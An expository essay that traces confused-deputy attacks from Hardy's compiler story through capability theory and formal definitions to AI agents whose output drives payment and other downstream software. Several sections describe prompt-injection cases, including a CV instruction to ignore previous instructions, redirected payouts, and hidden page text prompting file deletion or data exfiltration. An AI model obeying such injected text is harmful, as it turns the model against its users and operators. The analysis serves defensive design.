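# Confused-deputy attacks through AI agent output: how authority spreads into downstream software

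## Background: the confused deputy, capabilities and AI agents

In a confused-deputy attack, an attacker who lacks the authority to do something gets a program that has this authority to do it for them. The program, called the deputy, acts on requests or data from others using its own authority. The attacker only has to supply an input, often just a name, and does not need to break into the deputy or steal its credentials. The term comes from Norm Hardy's 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy*, which describes how a compiler on a commercial timesharing service destroyed the service's billing records. A familiar later case is cross-site request forgery, in which a hostile web page gets a visitor's browser to send requests under the visitor's login.

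The confused deputy problem now also arises with AI agents. An agent is a language model together with the software that turns the model's text into actions. Suppose an operator lets an agent write only one field of one record in a queue. If a payment program reads that field and sends money accordingly, the agent's text causes a payment even though the agent has no access to any account. The payment program plays roughly the same role as Hardy's compiler. It is a downstream program, meaning ordinary software that reads an agent's output and acts on it with rights the agent lacks.

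### The compiler and the billing file

Hardy presents the case as a "nearly true story" with inessential details changed. It happened in the late 1970s at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The service kept a compiler in a system directory, SYSX. Customers ran it with the command `RUN (SYSX)FORT` and could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics on which language features people used. It wrote them to a file in the same directory, (SYSX)STAT, whose name the programmers had built into the code. So that the compiler could write to this file, the operators gave it a right of its own, the "home files license", which let a program write files in its home directory.

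SYSX also held the billing file, (SYSX)BILL. A customer learned that name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for the debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system with a request to open the file for writing. The operating system opened it because the compiler had home files license. The company lost its billing records when the compiler wrote debugging information over them.

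The operating system checked only whether the compiler could write in SYSX. It could, so the check passed. The request did not record that the file name had come from a customer who had no right to write there.

Hardy could not blame the compiler's code either. A rule against writing to other directories would have removed a useful feature. A rule against writing to SYSX would have shut out people with legitimate access to that directory, and the name SYSX did not exist when the programmers wrote the code. A rule against writing to (SYSX)BILL would have left the other sensitive files in SYSX exposed and needed an update for each new one. Hardy argued that the code was correct until the operators granted the license, and that the operators would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file to see the danger. A narrower license would only have changed which file was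 at risk. If the compiler could write to (SYSX)STAT and nothing else in the directory, a customer could still have named (SYSX)STAT and wiped out the statistics.

Hardy traced the problem to the compiler running with authority from two sources, the customer who ran it and the license. It should have written the debugging output under the customer's authority and the statistics under the license, but it had no way to specify which authority it meant to use for which file. The developers first added a "switch hats" system call, which let a program choose one of its two authorities before opening a file. A request to open (SYSX)BILL under the customer's authority would then properly fail. This fix did not last well, because some applications needed more than two authorities and the system protected more than files. By Hardy's last count, the rule for when a program could open a file contained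 fourteen "ands" and "ors".

### Access-control lists, ambient authority and capabilities

Most operating systems decide such requests using access-control lists, or ACLs. For each file or other resource, the system keeps a list of who may do what with it. Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) counts Windows, macOS, Linux, iOS and Android among the systems that work this way, though the details vary.

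Access rights are usually pictured as a table, the access matrix, with a row for each user or program and a column for each resource. An ACL is one column of that table. A capability system is often pictured as the same table stored by rows, so that each program carries a list of the things it may use. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) rejects the common conclusion that the two designs hold the same information and differ only in how they store it. A static table leaves out how rights change over time and hides which way the references point. ACL entries point from the resource to the user, so a program needs a separate scheme, such as filenames, to designate the object an action applies to. In a capability system the entry points from the program to the resource, so a single entry can both designate the resource and carry the right to it.

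When a system separates naming an object from the right to use it, programs usually end up with ambient authority. A program exercises this authority merely by naming an object, because of the account it runs under. The Unix call `open()` is the standard example. The caller supplies a filename but does not choose a credential, and the call succeeds or fails according to the process's account. Miller and colleagues compare this to a world with doors but no keys, in which a door opens when the right person walks up. Someone entitled to pass for two reasons cannot invoke only one of them. The compiler was in this position when it opened the file that the customer had named.

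A capability is an unforgeable reference that both designates an object and carries the right to use it. In Hardy's capability version of the story, the compiler holds a capability to the statistics file, and the customer passes it a second capability for the debugging output. The compiler writes each kind of output through the matching capability, so it needs no filenames and the system has no list to consult. Knowing the name (SYSX)BILL does not give a customer a capability to that file, so the customer cannot pass one to the compiler. The compiler's author must still use each capability for its proper purpose, but the two are now distinct.

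### Two ways to copy a file

Ordinary Unix contains both styles, as Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, show with a pair of commands that have the same result. The first is:

`cp foo.txt bar.txt`

The shell, the program that reads the user's commands, hands `cp` two strings. They mean nothing until `cp` asks the operating system to open the files with those names, and `cp` cannot know in advance which names the user will type. So it has to be able to read and write any file that the user can. Even the least authority with which `cp` could do its job includes all of the user's authority over the file system. The second command is:

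`cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`

Here the shell opens both files before `cat` starts and passes it two file descriptors, which are handles to the open files. `cat` copies from one to the other without using either file's name. On a normal Unix system `cat` still runs with all of the user's authority, but it needs only the two descriptors for this job.

The same arrangement would have protected Tymshare's billing records. If the shell had opened the debugging file with the customer's own rights and passed the open file to the compiler, the attempt to open (SYSX)BILL would have failed before the compiler started. File descriptors are close to capabilities, but Miller and colleagues note that an ACL controls the Unix socket over which one process sends a descriptor to another.

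### The rules of the object-capability model

Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn proposed the original capability model in 1966. Miller and Shapiro restate it in the terms of object-oriented programming, under the name object-capability model. An object is a combination of code and state, and its state consists of references to other objects. Objects affect one another only by sending messages along references, and a message can carry further references as arguments. A reference combines the designation of an object, the permission to access it and the means of doing so, and no program can split these apart. (Permission here covers what a program may do directly to objects it can access, while authority also takes in the effects it can cause through other programs.)

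No program can forge a reference. An object can therefore come to hold one in only a few ways:

- Initial conditions: the reference was already there when the system started.
- Creation: an object that creates another receives the only reference to it, and can equip the new object with references from its own stock.
- Introduction: if Alice holds references to both Bob and Carol, she can send Bob a message that contains her reference to Carol. Bob can use Carol from then on.

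Miller and Shapiro summarise the consequence as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If no chain of references links two groups of objects, no code in either group can connect them, even if it is hostile. An analyst can therefore put an outer limit on what a program might reach by tracing references, without reading the program. The limit holds only if the language or operating system blocks every other way for objects to reach or communicate with each other. C++ does not, because a programmer can turn an integer into a pointer to any address. Ordinary Java does not either, because objects can communicate through shared static variables without holding references to each other.

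These protections do not cover plain data. A number or a string conveys information but not access, and any program that can work out its value can have it. Pathnames, which anyone can type, are plain data, and so is everything a language model writes.

### Agents, tool calls and prompt injection

A language model produces only text. Modular's *Agent harnesses* describes the harness as the software around the model that keeps the conversation, offers the model tools, carries out the actions the model requests and decides when to stop. A tool might search a mailbox, query a database or issue a refund.

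*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes the resulting loop as a conversation of alternating prompts and responses (p₁, r₁, p₂, r₂ and so on). The opening prompt p₁ contains the user's instruction. The model samples each response from a probability distribution that depends on the whole conversation so far. Some responses encode a tool call, which is the name of a tool with values for its arguments. The harness runs the tool and puts the result into the next prompt. A web page or email that the agent fetches therefore enters the conversation in the same form as the user's instructions and can influence every later response. Prompt injection occurs when such text unduly steers the model's output.

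In a 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs. A candidate hides an instruction in their CV for the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the application. In SQL, the language of database queries, a programmer can mark user input so that the database never interprets it as a command. Models have no equivalent because they only predict the next token from all the text so far. David C therefore describes models as "inherently confusable" deputies and advises designers to limit the harm a misled model can cause.

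A misled model matters most when the harness acts on its text without further checks. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, audited the public code of three widely used toolkits: LangChain with LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. In LangChain's classic design, a parser turns the model's text into a tool name and arguments, a dispatcher looks the name up in a table, and the tool runs. The software checks that the tool exists and commonly that the arguments have the right type. None of the three toolkits checked by default whether the argument values were allowed. In a demonstration with a mock merchant account, Mellafe Zuvic fed LangChain a fixed model output that redirected payouts to `acct_ATTACKER_999`, and the framework made the change. The value was a well-formed account number, just as (SYSX)BILL was a valid filename. Real models also produce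 such calls. In a related test of 27 models, injected text that posed as part of the user's task led 12 cheaper models to attempt an unauthorized call at a mean rate of about 60 percent, compared with 19 percent for 15 flagship models.

In those tests the harm comes through the agent's own tools, but the same text can also reach software outside the agent. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* (2025), guidance from an organisation that catalogues software vulnerabilities, lists applications that pass model output to a system shell, run it as a database query or build file paths from it. In one scenario, a chatbot passes its response unchecked to an extension with administrative functions, and the extension shuts down for maintenance, although the chatbot itself had no power to shut anything down. The file-path case is even closer to Tymshare, because one party again supplies the file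 name and another has permission to write the file.

### Three meanings of "capability"

In work on agent security, the word "capability" has several meanings besides its everyday sense of what a model can do.

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use "capability" to mean an unforgeable reference, as in the object-capability model. Their agent writes programs in a restricted form of Scala, where a capability is an ordinary value, such as an object through which code can reach the file system. The restricted language forbids the type casts and reflection that a program could otherwise use to get around the rules.

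In CaMeL, a defence against prompt injection from Google DeepMind, "capabilities" are metadata attached to values. According to *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), which extends that system, the metadata records which sources a value came from and who may read it. When the agent's program calls a tool, a policy function checks the metadata on the arguments and allows or denies the call. This can stop a payment to an account number that came from a stranger's email. "Provenance label" would be a more exact name, because the metadata doesn't grant any authority. A program that holds an account number from a trusted source still needs separate authority to send money there.

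Mellafe Zuvic's "capability gating" concerns which tools the harness offers to the model. A model that is offered a refund tool has a standing power to request refunds, and it fills in the amount and the recipient as plain data.

Some systems fall between these uses. *AgentCap* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) issues signed, short-lived tokens that name an agent, an action and a resource. An attacker cannot forge these tokens, which gives them one essential property of object capabilities. In the paper's banking example, however, a token authorizes one transfer within 30 seconds, while the model supplies the recipient separately, as an argument. This again separates the right to make the transfer from part of its designation, so the system must also check the recipient's provenance.

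From here on, "capability" means only the unforgeable reference.

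## Permission and authority: how far an agent's power reaches

An agent's access settings list what it may do directly, but not what other programs will do in response. In Miller and Shapiro's terms, the settings record the agent's permissions, while its authority also includes those further effects.

Their example is `/etc/passwd`, the file in which Unix keeps its list of user accounts. Alice has permission to read the file and Bob does not, but if Alice sends Bob copies of the text, he still has authority to read it. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006), a doctoral thesis that builds on the earlier paper, applies the distinction to writing. Bob has permission to message Alice, and Alice has permission to write to the file. Because Alice writes whatever text Bob asks for, Bob has authority to change a file that the operating system would not let him open. An administrator can look up both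 permissions, but no permission records that Alice writes what Bob asks for.

Alan Karp gave a shorter example in *Permity*, a mailing-list thread opened by Nicol (2026). Only the administrator and the web server have permission to read the file that holds a site's home page, but the server sends its contents to anyone who requests the page. Someone who looked only at permissions might mistakenly think the file was a safe place for secrets.

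The same gap appears in current coding agents. *AuthorityLens* (Chen, Jing and colleagues, 2026) lists 599 outcomes, such as deleting a file outside the agent's workspace or reading a credentials file, and identifies which of them each agent could bring about in each of its modes. In OpenCode's Plan mode, the main agent may not use the ordinary file-editing tool, but it can still run shell commands and hand work to other agents that can run them too. Plan mode allows the same 537 outcomes as Build mode. Gemini CLI's Plan mode removes the shell and allows only 76 outcomes, compared with 552 in its other modes.

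### De jure and de facto transfer

Miller and Shapiro adapted their distinction from Bishop and Snyder's *The Transfer of Information and Authority in a Protection System* (1979). Formal models of the time could determine whether a user might gain the right to read a file, but they did not cover other ways a user without that right might get the information.

Bishop and Snyder drew a system as a graph, with users and files as points and rights as arrows between them. In a de jure transfer, a user obtains information by using a right. For example, if Abel has the right to take rights from Baker, Abel can take Baker's right to read a file and then read it. In a de facto transfer, a user obtains the information without necessarily gaining the right. For example, Baker and Charlie share a mailbox file, and Charlie copies a private file into it at Baker's request. Baker can now read the copy but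 has no right to the original. The copy may be incomplete, and it won't show later changes to the original. The two kinds of transfer can also combine. If Abel takes Baker's right to read the mailbox, Abel can read Charlie's copy too, though Charlie may believe that only Baker will see it.

Bishop and Snyder wrote four rules to find such transfers systematically. The rules add dashed arrows to the graph to show possible access, but these arrows grant no rights. One rule covers the mailbox. If one user can write to a file and another can read it, the second can potentially read from the first. Another rule combines two reading steps into one. An algorithm can check, in time proportional to the size of the graph, whether any chain of these rules connects a given user to a given file.

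The four rules deal with reading, whereas an agent that writes to a queue causes effects in the other direction. Bishop and Snyder showed that the same results hold for writing if "read" and "write" are swapped throughout. They were still describing how information moves. Miller and Shapiro extended the idea to access rights, and so to the effects a program can have on objects.

### Where the system's boundary lies

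Any statement about permissions assumes a boundary between a base system and the programs that run on it. The base system, such as an operating system kernel, sets the rules, and the programs can act only as those rules allow. Miller and Shapiro call this boundary the frame of reference, and changing the frame can turn authority into permission.

Miller and Shapiro give the example of a one-way channel. Cassie runs two untrusted programs, Q and Bond, and wants Q to be able to send numbers to Bond with nothing coming back. She writes a few lines of code that create a shared variable and two small objects. Q gets the object that can only write integers to the variable, and Bond gets the one that can only read them. At the level of the base system, Q has permission to send messages to the writing object and authority to send integers to Bond. If Cassie instead treats the channel as part of the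 system on which Q and Bond run, Q has permission to send integers to Bond. Miller and Shapiro conclude that permission depends on the frame of reference but authority does not, since Q can cause the same effects under both descriptions.

The same applies to the agent that may write one field in a queue. Within the database that stores the queue, the agent has permission to update a field. If the operator counts the database and the payment program as a single refund service, the agent has permission to request refunds. An auditor could truthfully report either permission. The first sounds much less serious, but the agent can move the same amount of money in both cases.

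Authority stays the same when the description changes, but it can change over time. Karp pointed out in the *Permity* thread that a program's authority changes when the object it invokes starts to behave differently, even if the program's permissions do not. So a new release of the payment program can increase the agent's authority even if no one changes the agent's settings.

### Two kinds of bound

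Calculating an agent's authority exactly would require predicting what every program that might react to its output will do, which Miller calls intractable. The practical alternative is an upper bound, a set of effects that includes everything the agent can cause and possibly more.

The simpler bound is an outer limit, found by tracing who can reach whom. Miller and Shapiro say it can give either a reliable "no" or a "maybe". If no chain of permitted interactions leads from the agent to an account, the answer is "no". If there is a chain, the answer is "maybe", because the agent can affect the account only if each program along the way passes the influence on, and the permissions alone don't show whether they do. Bishop and Snyder openly accepted this limitation and assumed that every user cooperates perfectly, which they called prudent but perhaps not very realistic.

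*A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (Parisel, 2026) applies this kind of analysis to companies that run many agents. It draws an arrow from one agent to another if the first can write to a resource that the second can read. A direct communication link counts in both directions, because even a reply can carry a prompt injection. An agent's "effective autonomy" includes the actions of every agent it can reach along the arrows. Parisel presents this as a measure of exposure and does not claim that each path leads to a real effect. The method also scores each link by how sensitive and how widely separated the resources involved are, and drops links that score below a threshold that the security team chooses. If the threshold is above zero, the absence of a path no longer reliably rules out an effect, since a dropped link can still carry one.

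The tighter bound also accounts for what some of the programs do. If we consider only reachability, Q could send a capability through Cassie's one-way channel, and Bond could use it to send something back. Cassie's code prevents this by accepting only integers.

A list of permissions errs in the opposite direction. Suppose Alice wants to give Bob access to Carol and be able to withdraw it later. Alice gives Bob a forwarding object, known as a Caretaker, which passes Bob's messages on to Carol until Alice switches it off. A security officer who asks for everyone with permission to access Carol will get a list without Bob on it, because Bob has permission only to use the forwarder. Miller therefore classes all bounds on permission as unsafe for deciding whether Bob can affect Carol. For authority, the thesis ranks the possibilities like this:

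actual authority ⊆ behavioural bound ⊆ reachability bound

Both bounds are safe because neither leaves out a real effect. The reachability bound is easy to compute, but people who rely on it reject many harmless arrangements. Computing the behavioural bound takes more work, but it lets them accept more of these arrangements.

*Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) defines these informal notions precisely. *Object-Capability as a Means of Permission and Authority in Software Systems* (Koepe, 2019) summarises the definitions, including the behavioural bound, which starts from a description B of how the program may behave. An analyst collects every state that B allows the system to reach and works out what an object could affect in any of them. The bound also holds for the real program P if P does only what B allows, because P can then reach only those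 states. Otherwise, the bound may be wrong.

The analyst must also decide whose behaviour to rely on. Miller and Shapiro advise using reachability alone for potential adversaries, and behaviour for programs that the analyst has reason to understand, such as the Caretaker. A language model that reads strangers' emails should be treated as a potential adversary. Injected text may lead it to write anything its interface accepts, so a safe bound has to allow for every possible output. Only the behaviour of the programs that read the output can tighten that bound.

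### A support agent and a dispatcher

In this invented example, a company's support agent reads customer emails. The only change it has permission to make is appending records to a queue. Each record contains an order number and a route, which must be `refund`, `replace`, `account`, `technical` or `other`. A dispatcher, an ordinary program with the right to issue refunds and change customer accounts, reads each record and acts on it. The company has 10,000 orders on file.

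The agent can output only 50,000 different records, one for each combination of five routes and 10,000 order numbers, so each record carries less than 16 bits of information.

Bishop and Snyder's rules for writing apply here in two steps. The agent can write to the queue and the dispatcher can read it, so the first step adds a dashed "write" arrow from the agent to the dispatcher. The dispatcher can write to the payment system and the accounts, so the second step extends the arrow to them. The graph doesn't include routes or order numbers, so by reachability alone, the agent and anyone who can email the company can do everything the dispatcher can, including issuing a refund of any size and changing any account.

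Suppose an engineer reads the dispatcher's code and finds that it will refund at most $200 in total on any one order. The agent can then make it pay out at most 10,000 × $200 = $2,000,000. If the code also stops after 50 refunds a day, the worst case is 50 × $200 = $10,000 a day. The daily limit gives the company time to notice, though the agent could still reach the full $2,000,000 after 200 days.

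Neither figure depends on the model's behavior, so both hold even if an attacker controls every record the agent writes. They do depend on how the dispatcher works. If the $200 limit applied to each refund instead of each order, and the dispatcher accepted repeated records for the same order, the agent could exceed $2,000,000. The check must also work on every input. Mellafe Zuvic built ScopeGate, a checking layer for agent tool calls that includes a ceiling on payments. In an early prototype, the comparison with the ceiling let through NaN, the value computers use for "not a number". A worst case calculated from the intended ceiling would have relied on a limit that the code did not fully enforce.

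The engineer also has to read the other routes. *Reasoning about External Calls* (Drossopoulou, Mackay and colleagues, 2025) shows why with the example of a shop that passes its account to a customer's unknown code to receive a payment. The shop needs to be sure that this code cannot empty the account. Withdrawals require a key, so the account is safe if the customer has no access to the key and the shop's code never leaks it. In one version of the program, however, any caller can replace the key and then withdraw the money. The withdrawal method is the same as in the safe versions, so reading it alone would not reveal the flaw. In the support example, an `account` route that could raise a customer's refund limit would undo the $200 cap in the same way. Even without that flaw, the dollar figures cover only refunds, so the company would need a separate bound on changes to accounts.

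An agent with a narrow output type can still have broad authority. The record's type limited the agent to valid routes and order numbers, but the dispatcher's code determined what each record could do. If the company added a free-text comment of 10,000 characters and the dispatcher ignored it, the agent's authority would not grow. A single yes-or-no field could give the agent more authority than the whole record if some program treated "yes" as an instruction to refund every order in full. Replacing the order number with a capability would restrict which orders the agent could designate, but the dispatcher's code would still determine what happened to them.

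### Output that a person reads, and output that nobody reads

Suppose the company replaces the dispatcher with an employee who reads the records on a screen. In Miller and Shapiro's model, people are outside the computational system, and programs can affect the outside world only by sending messages to output devices. The analysis can establish that the agent's records reach the screen, but not what happens next, since the employee might ignore a record, issue a refund or phone a colleague. The agent may well have authority over refunds in this arrangement, but there is no code from which to derive a limit on what the employee does.

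A firm limit has to come from the software the employee uses next. If the refund tool enforces the same limits of $200 per refund and 50 refunds a day, refunds made through it cannot exceed $10,000 a day, even if the employee approves every record without reading it.

Chen and colleagues measured how many of the 599 outcomes are possible in different modes of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. In full-access mode, the model can bring about all 599 alone. In the mode that asks the user for approval, 597 are still possible, but 279 of those require both the model and the user. The protection that approval provides therefore depends on the user refusing harmful requests.

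If the records instead go to a file that no person or program reads, the agent has no authority through that file, even if it may write free text of any length. In Miller and Shapiro's model, effects travel only along permitted paths, and here the path ends at the file. The company must make sure that nothing reads the file, including search indexers and scheduled imports into other systems. If an administrator later lets a program read the file and act on it, the agent gains authority even though its own permissions have not changed.

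Even a reliable "no" rules out only overt causation, meaning effects that pass through the channels in the model. Miller and Shapiro leave out covert channels, through which programs communicate using something the system's designers did not intend for communication. For example, an agent that writes to the unread file in bursts might slow the disk in a pattern that another program can detect, and the reachability graph has no arrow for this effect.

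## What counts as a confused-deputy attack

In the support example, the dispatcher pays refunds based on records an agent writes, and the company wants to pay most of those refunds. A definition of a confused-deputy attack has to separate this normal use of a deputy from misuse. Researchers have proposed several definitions, which disagree about some of the cases that matter most for agents.

### A program with a hole for the attacker

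Rajani, Garg and Rezk (2016), in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, gave what they believed to be the first formal definition of a program free from these attacks. In their small programming language, each step of a program runs with the authority of one principal, such as a user or a service. Every stored object has an owner, and a step may write to an object only if the step's principal ranks at least as high as the object's owner.

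One step is a hole, which the attacker can fill with any commands. These run with the attacker's own authority. The analyst also names a set of objects that the attacker wants to change. For a given starting state, the program is free from confused-deputy attacks if, whatever commands the attacker chooses, every object in the set meets at least one of two conditions:

- No adversary control: the object would have ended with the same value if the attacker had chosen any other commands.
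- Direct adversary write: the attacker could have given the object that value by running some commands alone, without the rest of the program.

In symbols, let E[c](r) be the final value of object r when program E runs with commands c in the hole, and let A[c](r) be its final value when c runs alone. Then for every c and every r in the set:

(for all c′, E[c′](r) = E[c](r)) or (for some c″, A[c″](r) = E[c](r))

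An attack is possible when some choice of commands produces a run that finishes and leaves an object with a value for which both conditions fail. If the first condition holds, the attacker has no influence over the object, and if the second holds, the attacker does not need a deputy.

The definition depends only on a comparison of final values, not on how the program produced them. It therefore covers both an attacker who chooses which file the deputy writes to and one who can choose only what the deputy writes there.

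### The compiler as a two-step program

Rajani and colleagues first apply the definition to a simplified compiler, which in slightly altered notation looks like this:

`⊥{ • } ∘ ⊤{ !out := compile(!src) }`

The dot marks the hole. The caller runs first, with the lowest authority (⊥), and the compiler runs second, with the highest (⊤). The caller may write to two objects: `src`, which holds the source program, and `out`, which holds a reference to the output file. The exclamation mark means "read the contents of", so the compiler compiles whatever is in `src` and writes the result to whichever file `out` refers to.

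Suppose the attacker wants to damage a file called `target`, which the caller has no right to write to. The attacker fills the hole with these commands:

`out := target; src := s1`

The compiler then overwrites `target` with the compiled form of program s1. The first condition fails because the file would have had different contents if the attacker had supplied a different program, s2. The second condition also fails because the caller's commands alone could only have left `target` as it was, and it did not already contain the compiled form of s1. Since both conditions fail, this compiler is open to attack.

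That happens under ordinary access control. Under the capability rules in the same paper, the caller cannot get a write reference to `target`, so the run stops before the compiler starts.

### Endorsement and the billing file

The full version of the example differs a little from Hardy's story. In Hardy's account the compiler had no reason to touch the billing file. In the version that Rajani and colleagues use, the compiler itself records there what each caller owes:

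`⊥{ • } ∘ ⊤{ !out := compile(!src) } ∘ ⊤*{ bill := billing(!src) }`

Setting aside the asterisk, the compiler would still fail the definition even if someone fixed the problem with the output file. If program s1 costs $3 to compile and program s2 costs $5, the caller's choice between them changes the final value of `bill`, which the caller has no right to write to. Both conditions fail, even though the company wants larger jobs to produce larger bills.

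Rajani and colleagues therefore let the programmer mark a step as endorsed, shown here by the asterisk, when the deputy is deliberately letting a less trusted party influence the result. The revised definition applies the two conditions to every unbroken series of steps that contains no endorsed step. In the full compiler, the billing step is exempt, and the first two steps are tested together and fail because of the output file.

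The exemption relies entirely on the programmer's judgment. If the `billing` function let callers state their own price in a comment, the revised definition would exempt that too. Askarov and Myers (2011) made the general point in *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity* that it is hard to say what security remains once a language lets programmers endorse data. They proposed measuring the influence an attacker still has over trusted locations.

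The order of the steps also matters. Suppose the compiler sends the bill first:

`⊥{ • } ∘ ⊤*{ bill := billing(!src) } ∘ ⊤{ !out := compile(!src) }`

The endorsed step now comes between the attacker and the compile step, so the definition tests the compile step separately. With no attacker commands before it, the compile step always gives the same result from the same starting state, so the first condition holds. The program passes, even though under ordinary access control a caller can still name the billing file as the output and destroy the bill. Anyone who relies on the revised definition has to check separately what influence an attacker can have across an endorsed step.

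### How this differs from information-flow integrity

The usual standard for information-flow integrity is noninterference, which here means that nothing an attacker can write affects an object the attacker cannot write. To test it, an analyst compares runs with different attacker commands and different starting values in the objects the attacker can write. The program passes if the protected objects always end up the same.

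Rajani and colleagues prove that any program in their language that passes this test is also free from confused-deputy attacks. The reverse is not true, as this one-step program shows:

`⊤{ ledger := !inbox }`

The attacker can write to `inbox` but not to `ledger`. Changing the initial value of `inbox` changes the final value of `ledger`, so the program violates noninterference. It is still free from confused-deputy attacks under the 2016 definition, because it has no hole and the definition considers one starting state at a time.

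The difference matters for any program that reads a queue. An analyst who examines only the support dispatcher, with records already waiting, will find no confused-deputy attack, whatever the dispatcher does with them. For a meaningful answer, the analyst has to include the step in which the agent writes the records, and place the hole at or before that step.

### Definitions based on who holds which right

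Two papers from 2026 use simpler definitions that compare permissions instead of possible runs. Gallo (2026), in *Proof-of-Continuity*, says that a confused deputy occurs when four things are true:

- The user lacks a certain privilege.
- The deputy has it.
- The user sends the deputy a request.
- The deputy exercises the privilege as a consequence.

*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) applies the idea to agents, defining the attack as one in which an agent accesses a resource that it has permission to use but the authenticated user does not. In its example, an employee asks an agent to show everyone's salaries, and the agent queries the HR database, which the employee isn't allowed to read.

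Both definitions also cover the compiler's normal billing, because the caller's request leads the compiler to update a billing file that it may write to but the caller may not. They likewise make every ordinary run of Hardy's compiler an attack, since each run updated a statistics file that customers could not write to. Siu and colleagues add that the agent in such a case fails to recognize that it should be using the user's permissions. This requirement would exclude the billing step, where the compiler is right to use its own permissions, but their formal condition omits it.

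Later in *Proof-of-Continuity*, Gallo addresses the problem by considering what a requester is entitled to cause, as well as what the requester may do directly. A bank customer cannot operate the bank's systems but may be entitled to have a payment gateway move money, so that transfer is legitimate delegation. The compiler updates its statistics as part of its own housekeeping, so that is not an attack either. An attack occurs when the requester designates a target and the deputy acts on it in a way the requester was not entitled to cause.

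Under this wording, the billing step is not an attack, because the compiler's programmers chose the billing file. The accompanying formula, however, includes only the missing right and the causal link, so the billing step still counts as an attack under the formula. The wording also excludes too much. A caller who can set the price in a comment chooses only the amount, not the target, so this would not count as an attack. Under the 2016 definition it would, unless the programmer had endorsed the step. Gallo also leaves open how a system should distinguish actions caused by a request from those the deputy started itself.

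*Type-Confusion Security* (Ren, Chen and colleagues, 2026) defines the attack in terms of function calls. In its example, a currency exchange collects each user's payment by calling a function that the user supplies. An attacker supplies the exchange's own `pay` function, so the exchange pays the attacker instead of collecting money. Each function's type specifies how trusted the calling code must be, and an attack is a call from a context less trusted than the type requires. The exchange's own code may call `pay` by name, but a call through a user-supplied function counts as untrusted.

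A compiler written in this style could call its own billing function without the call counting as an attack. Its programmers would still have to declare that untrusted callers may run the compiler even though it changes trusted data. Ren and colleagues treat such a declaration as a form of endorsement and consider it unavoidable. Ordinary applications, for instance, must be able to change an operating system's state through system calls.

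### When the user holds every right

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize a web page, and the agent runs with all of the user's rights. Hidden text in the page leads the agent to delete the user's files. The user had the right to delete them, so the agent did only what the user could have done.

Under the 2016 definition, this is an attack. The agent is the deputy, the page's author is the attacker, and the page's text fills the hole. The author caused a change to files that the author could not have changed directly.

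Siu and colleagues would not call this a confused-deputy attack, because the user has permission to delete the files. They class it as indirect prompt injection, which in their framework requires an instruction from an unauthenticated source and an action that does not serve the user's task. Under the four conditions in *Proof-of-Continuity*, the answer depends on who counts as the requester. If it is the user, no attack occurs, because the user has the right to delete the files. The page's author lacks that right, but is the requester only if a fetched web page counts as a request.

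*Beyond Proof of Possession* (Gallo, 2026) instead defines an attack by the rights attached to the request, which may be fewer than the rights the user holds. If the request carries only the right to summarize a page, deleting files is an attack even though the user could have deleted them. This works only if someone has limited the request's rights in advance. If a user asks an agent to pay an invoice and hidden text changes the recipient, the request already carries the right to transfer money from the user's account, so the definition doesn't count the transfer as an attack unless the request also limits who can receive the money. A later paper, *Full Provenance on the COSS Causal Axis* (Gallo, 2026), acknowledges that this definition and the 2016 one are not equivalent.

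Other authors use the term more broadly. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) applies it whenever injected content manipulates an agent into using legitimate authority for an attacker's goal: "The agent is authorized; the use is not intended." This definition clearly includes the deleted files and the redirected payment, but an analyst has to judge what the user intended, because permission lists don't record it.

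*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) also describes the agent as the deputy. It notes that the uncertainty here is about what the user wanted, whereas in traditional cases it is about which party the deputy is serving. In the paper's experiment, a user asked an agent to summarize a page whose metadata contained instructions to send sensitive data from the agent's context to an attacker's server. The agent, which ran on a small open-weight model, sent data in about 89 percent of 480 runs.

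The 2016 definition does not cover this kind of theft because it deals only with changes to objects. The stolen data ends up on the attacker's server, where the attacker can write anything. The attacker could have used some command to write the same data there directly, which satisfies the second condition even though the attacker did not know what to write.

These disagreements come mostly from comparing the deputy's authority with that of different people. Here it should be compared with the authority of the page's author rather than the user's, because the author chose the action and had no right to take it.

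### When only the downstream program holds the right

In the support example, the agent may add records to a queue but cannot access any account. Suppose a customer's email leads the agent to request a refund for someone else's order, and the dispatcher pays it. The dispatcher is the deputy for the payment. The agent is also a deputy, but only for writing to the queue, which the customer could not do directly.

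*Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) describes nearly the same pattern. An agent without permission for an action asks an agent that has permission to carry it out, and the second agent accepts the request as legitimate. The paper notes that the pattern is not specific to AI agents, so an ordinary program such as the dispatcher can take the second agent's place.

The condition Siu and colleagues use does not cover the payment, because it requires the agent itself to have permission to access the resource. The agent only writes to the queue, which it has permission to do. An analyst could make the condition cover the payment by treating the agent and the dispatcher as one system, which then has permission to pay, so the result depends on where the analyst draws the system's boundary.

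The four conditions in *Proof-of-Continuity* cover this case if a queue record counts as a request. The agent lacks the right to make payments, the dispatcher has it, and the record causes the payment. But a legitimate refund meets the same conditions. The difference is whether the customer was entitled to the refund. A customer who returned order 1001 is entitled to a refund for that order but not for order 2002. The dispatcher cannot check this because the record contains only an order number and a route.

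A confused-deputy attack can succeed even with a valid credential. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) gives the example of an agent that a user has authorized only to summarize invoices from an inbox. An email in the inbox contains a payment request, and the agent passes it to a finance agent without passing on the read-only restriction. The payment tool receives a valid credential and makes the payment. The tool can check who is calling, but it can't detect that the email led the first agent to exceed its task.

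A queue can also hide the connection between a request and its effect. The definition in *Beyond Proof of Possession* covers any effect that a request causes, including one that passes through a queue. But Gallo concedes that the paper's enforcement method can fail to connect the effect to the original request if a background program reads the queue later and starts a new chain of actions.

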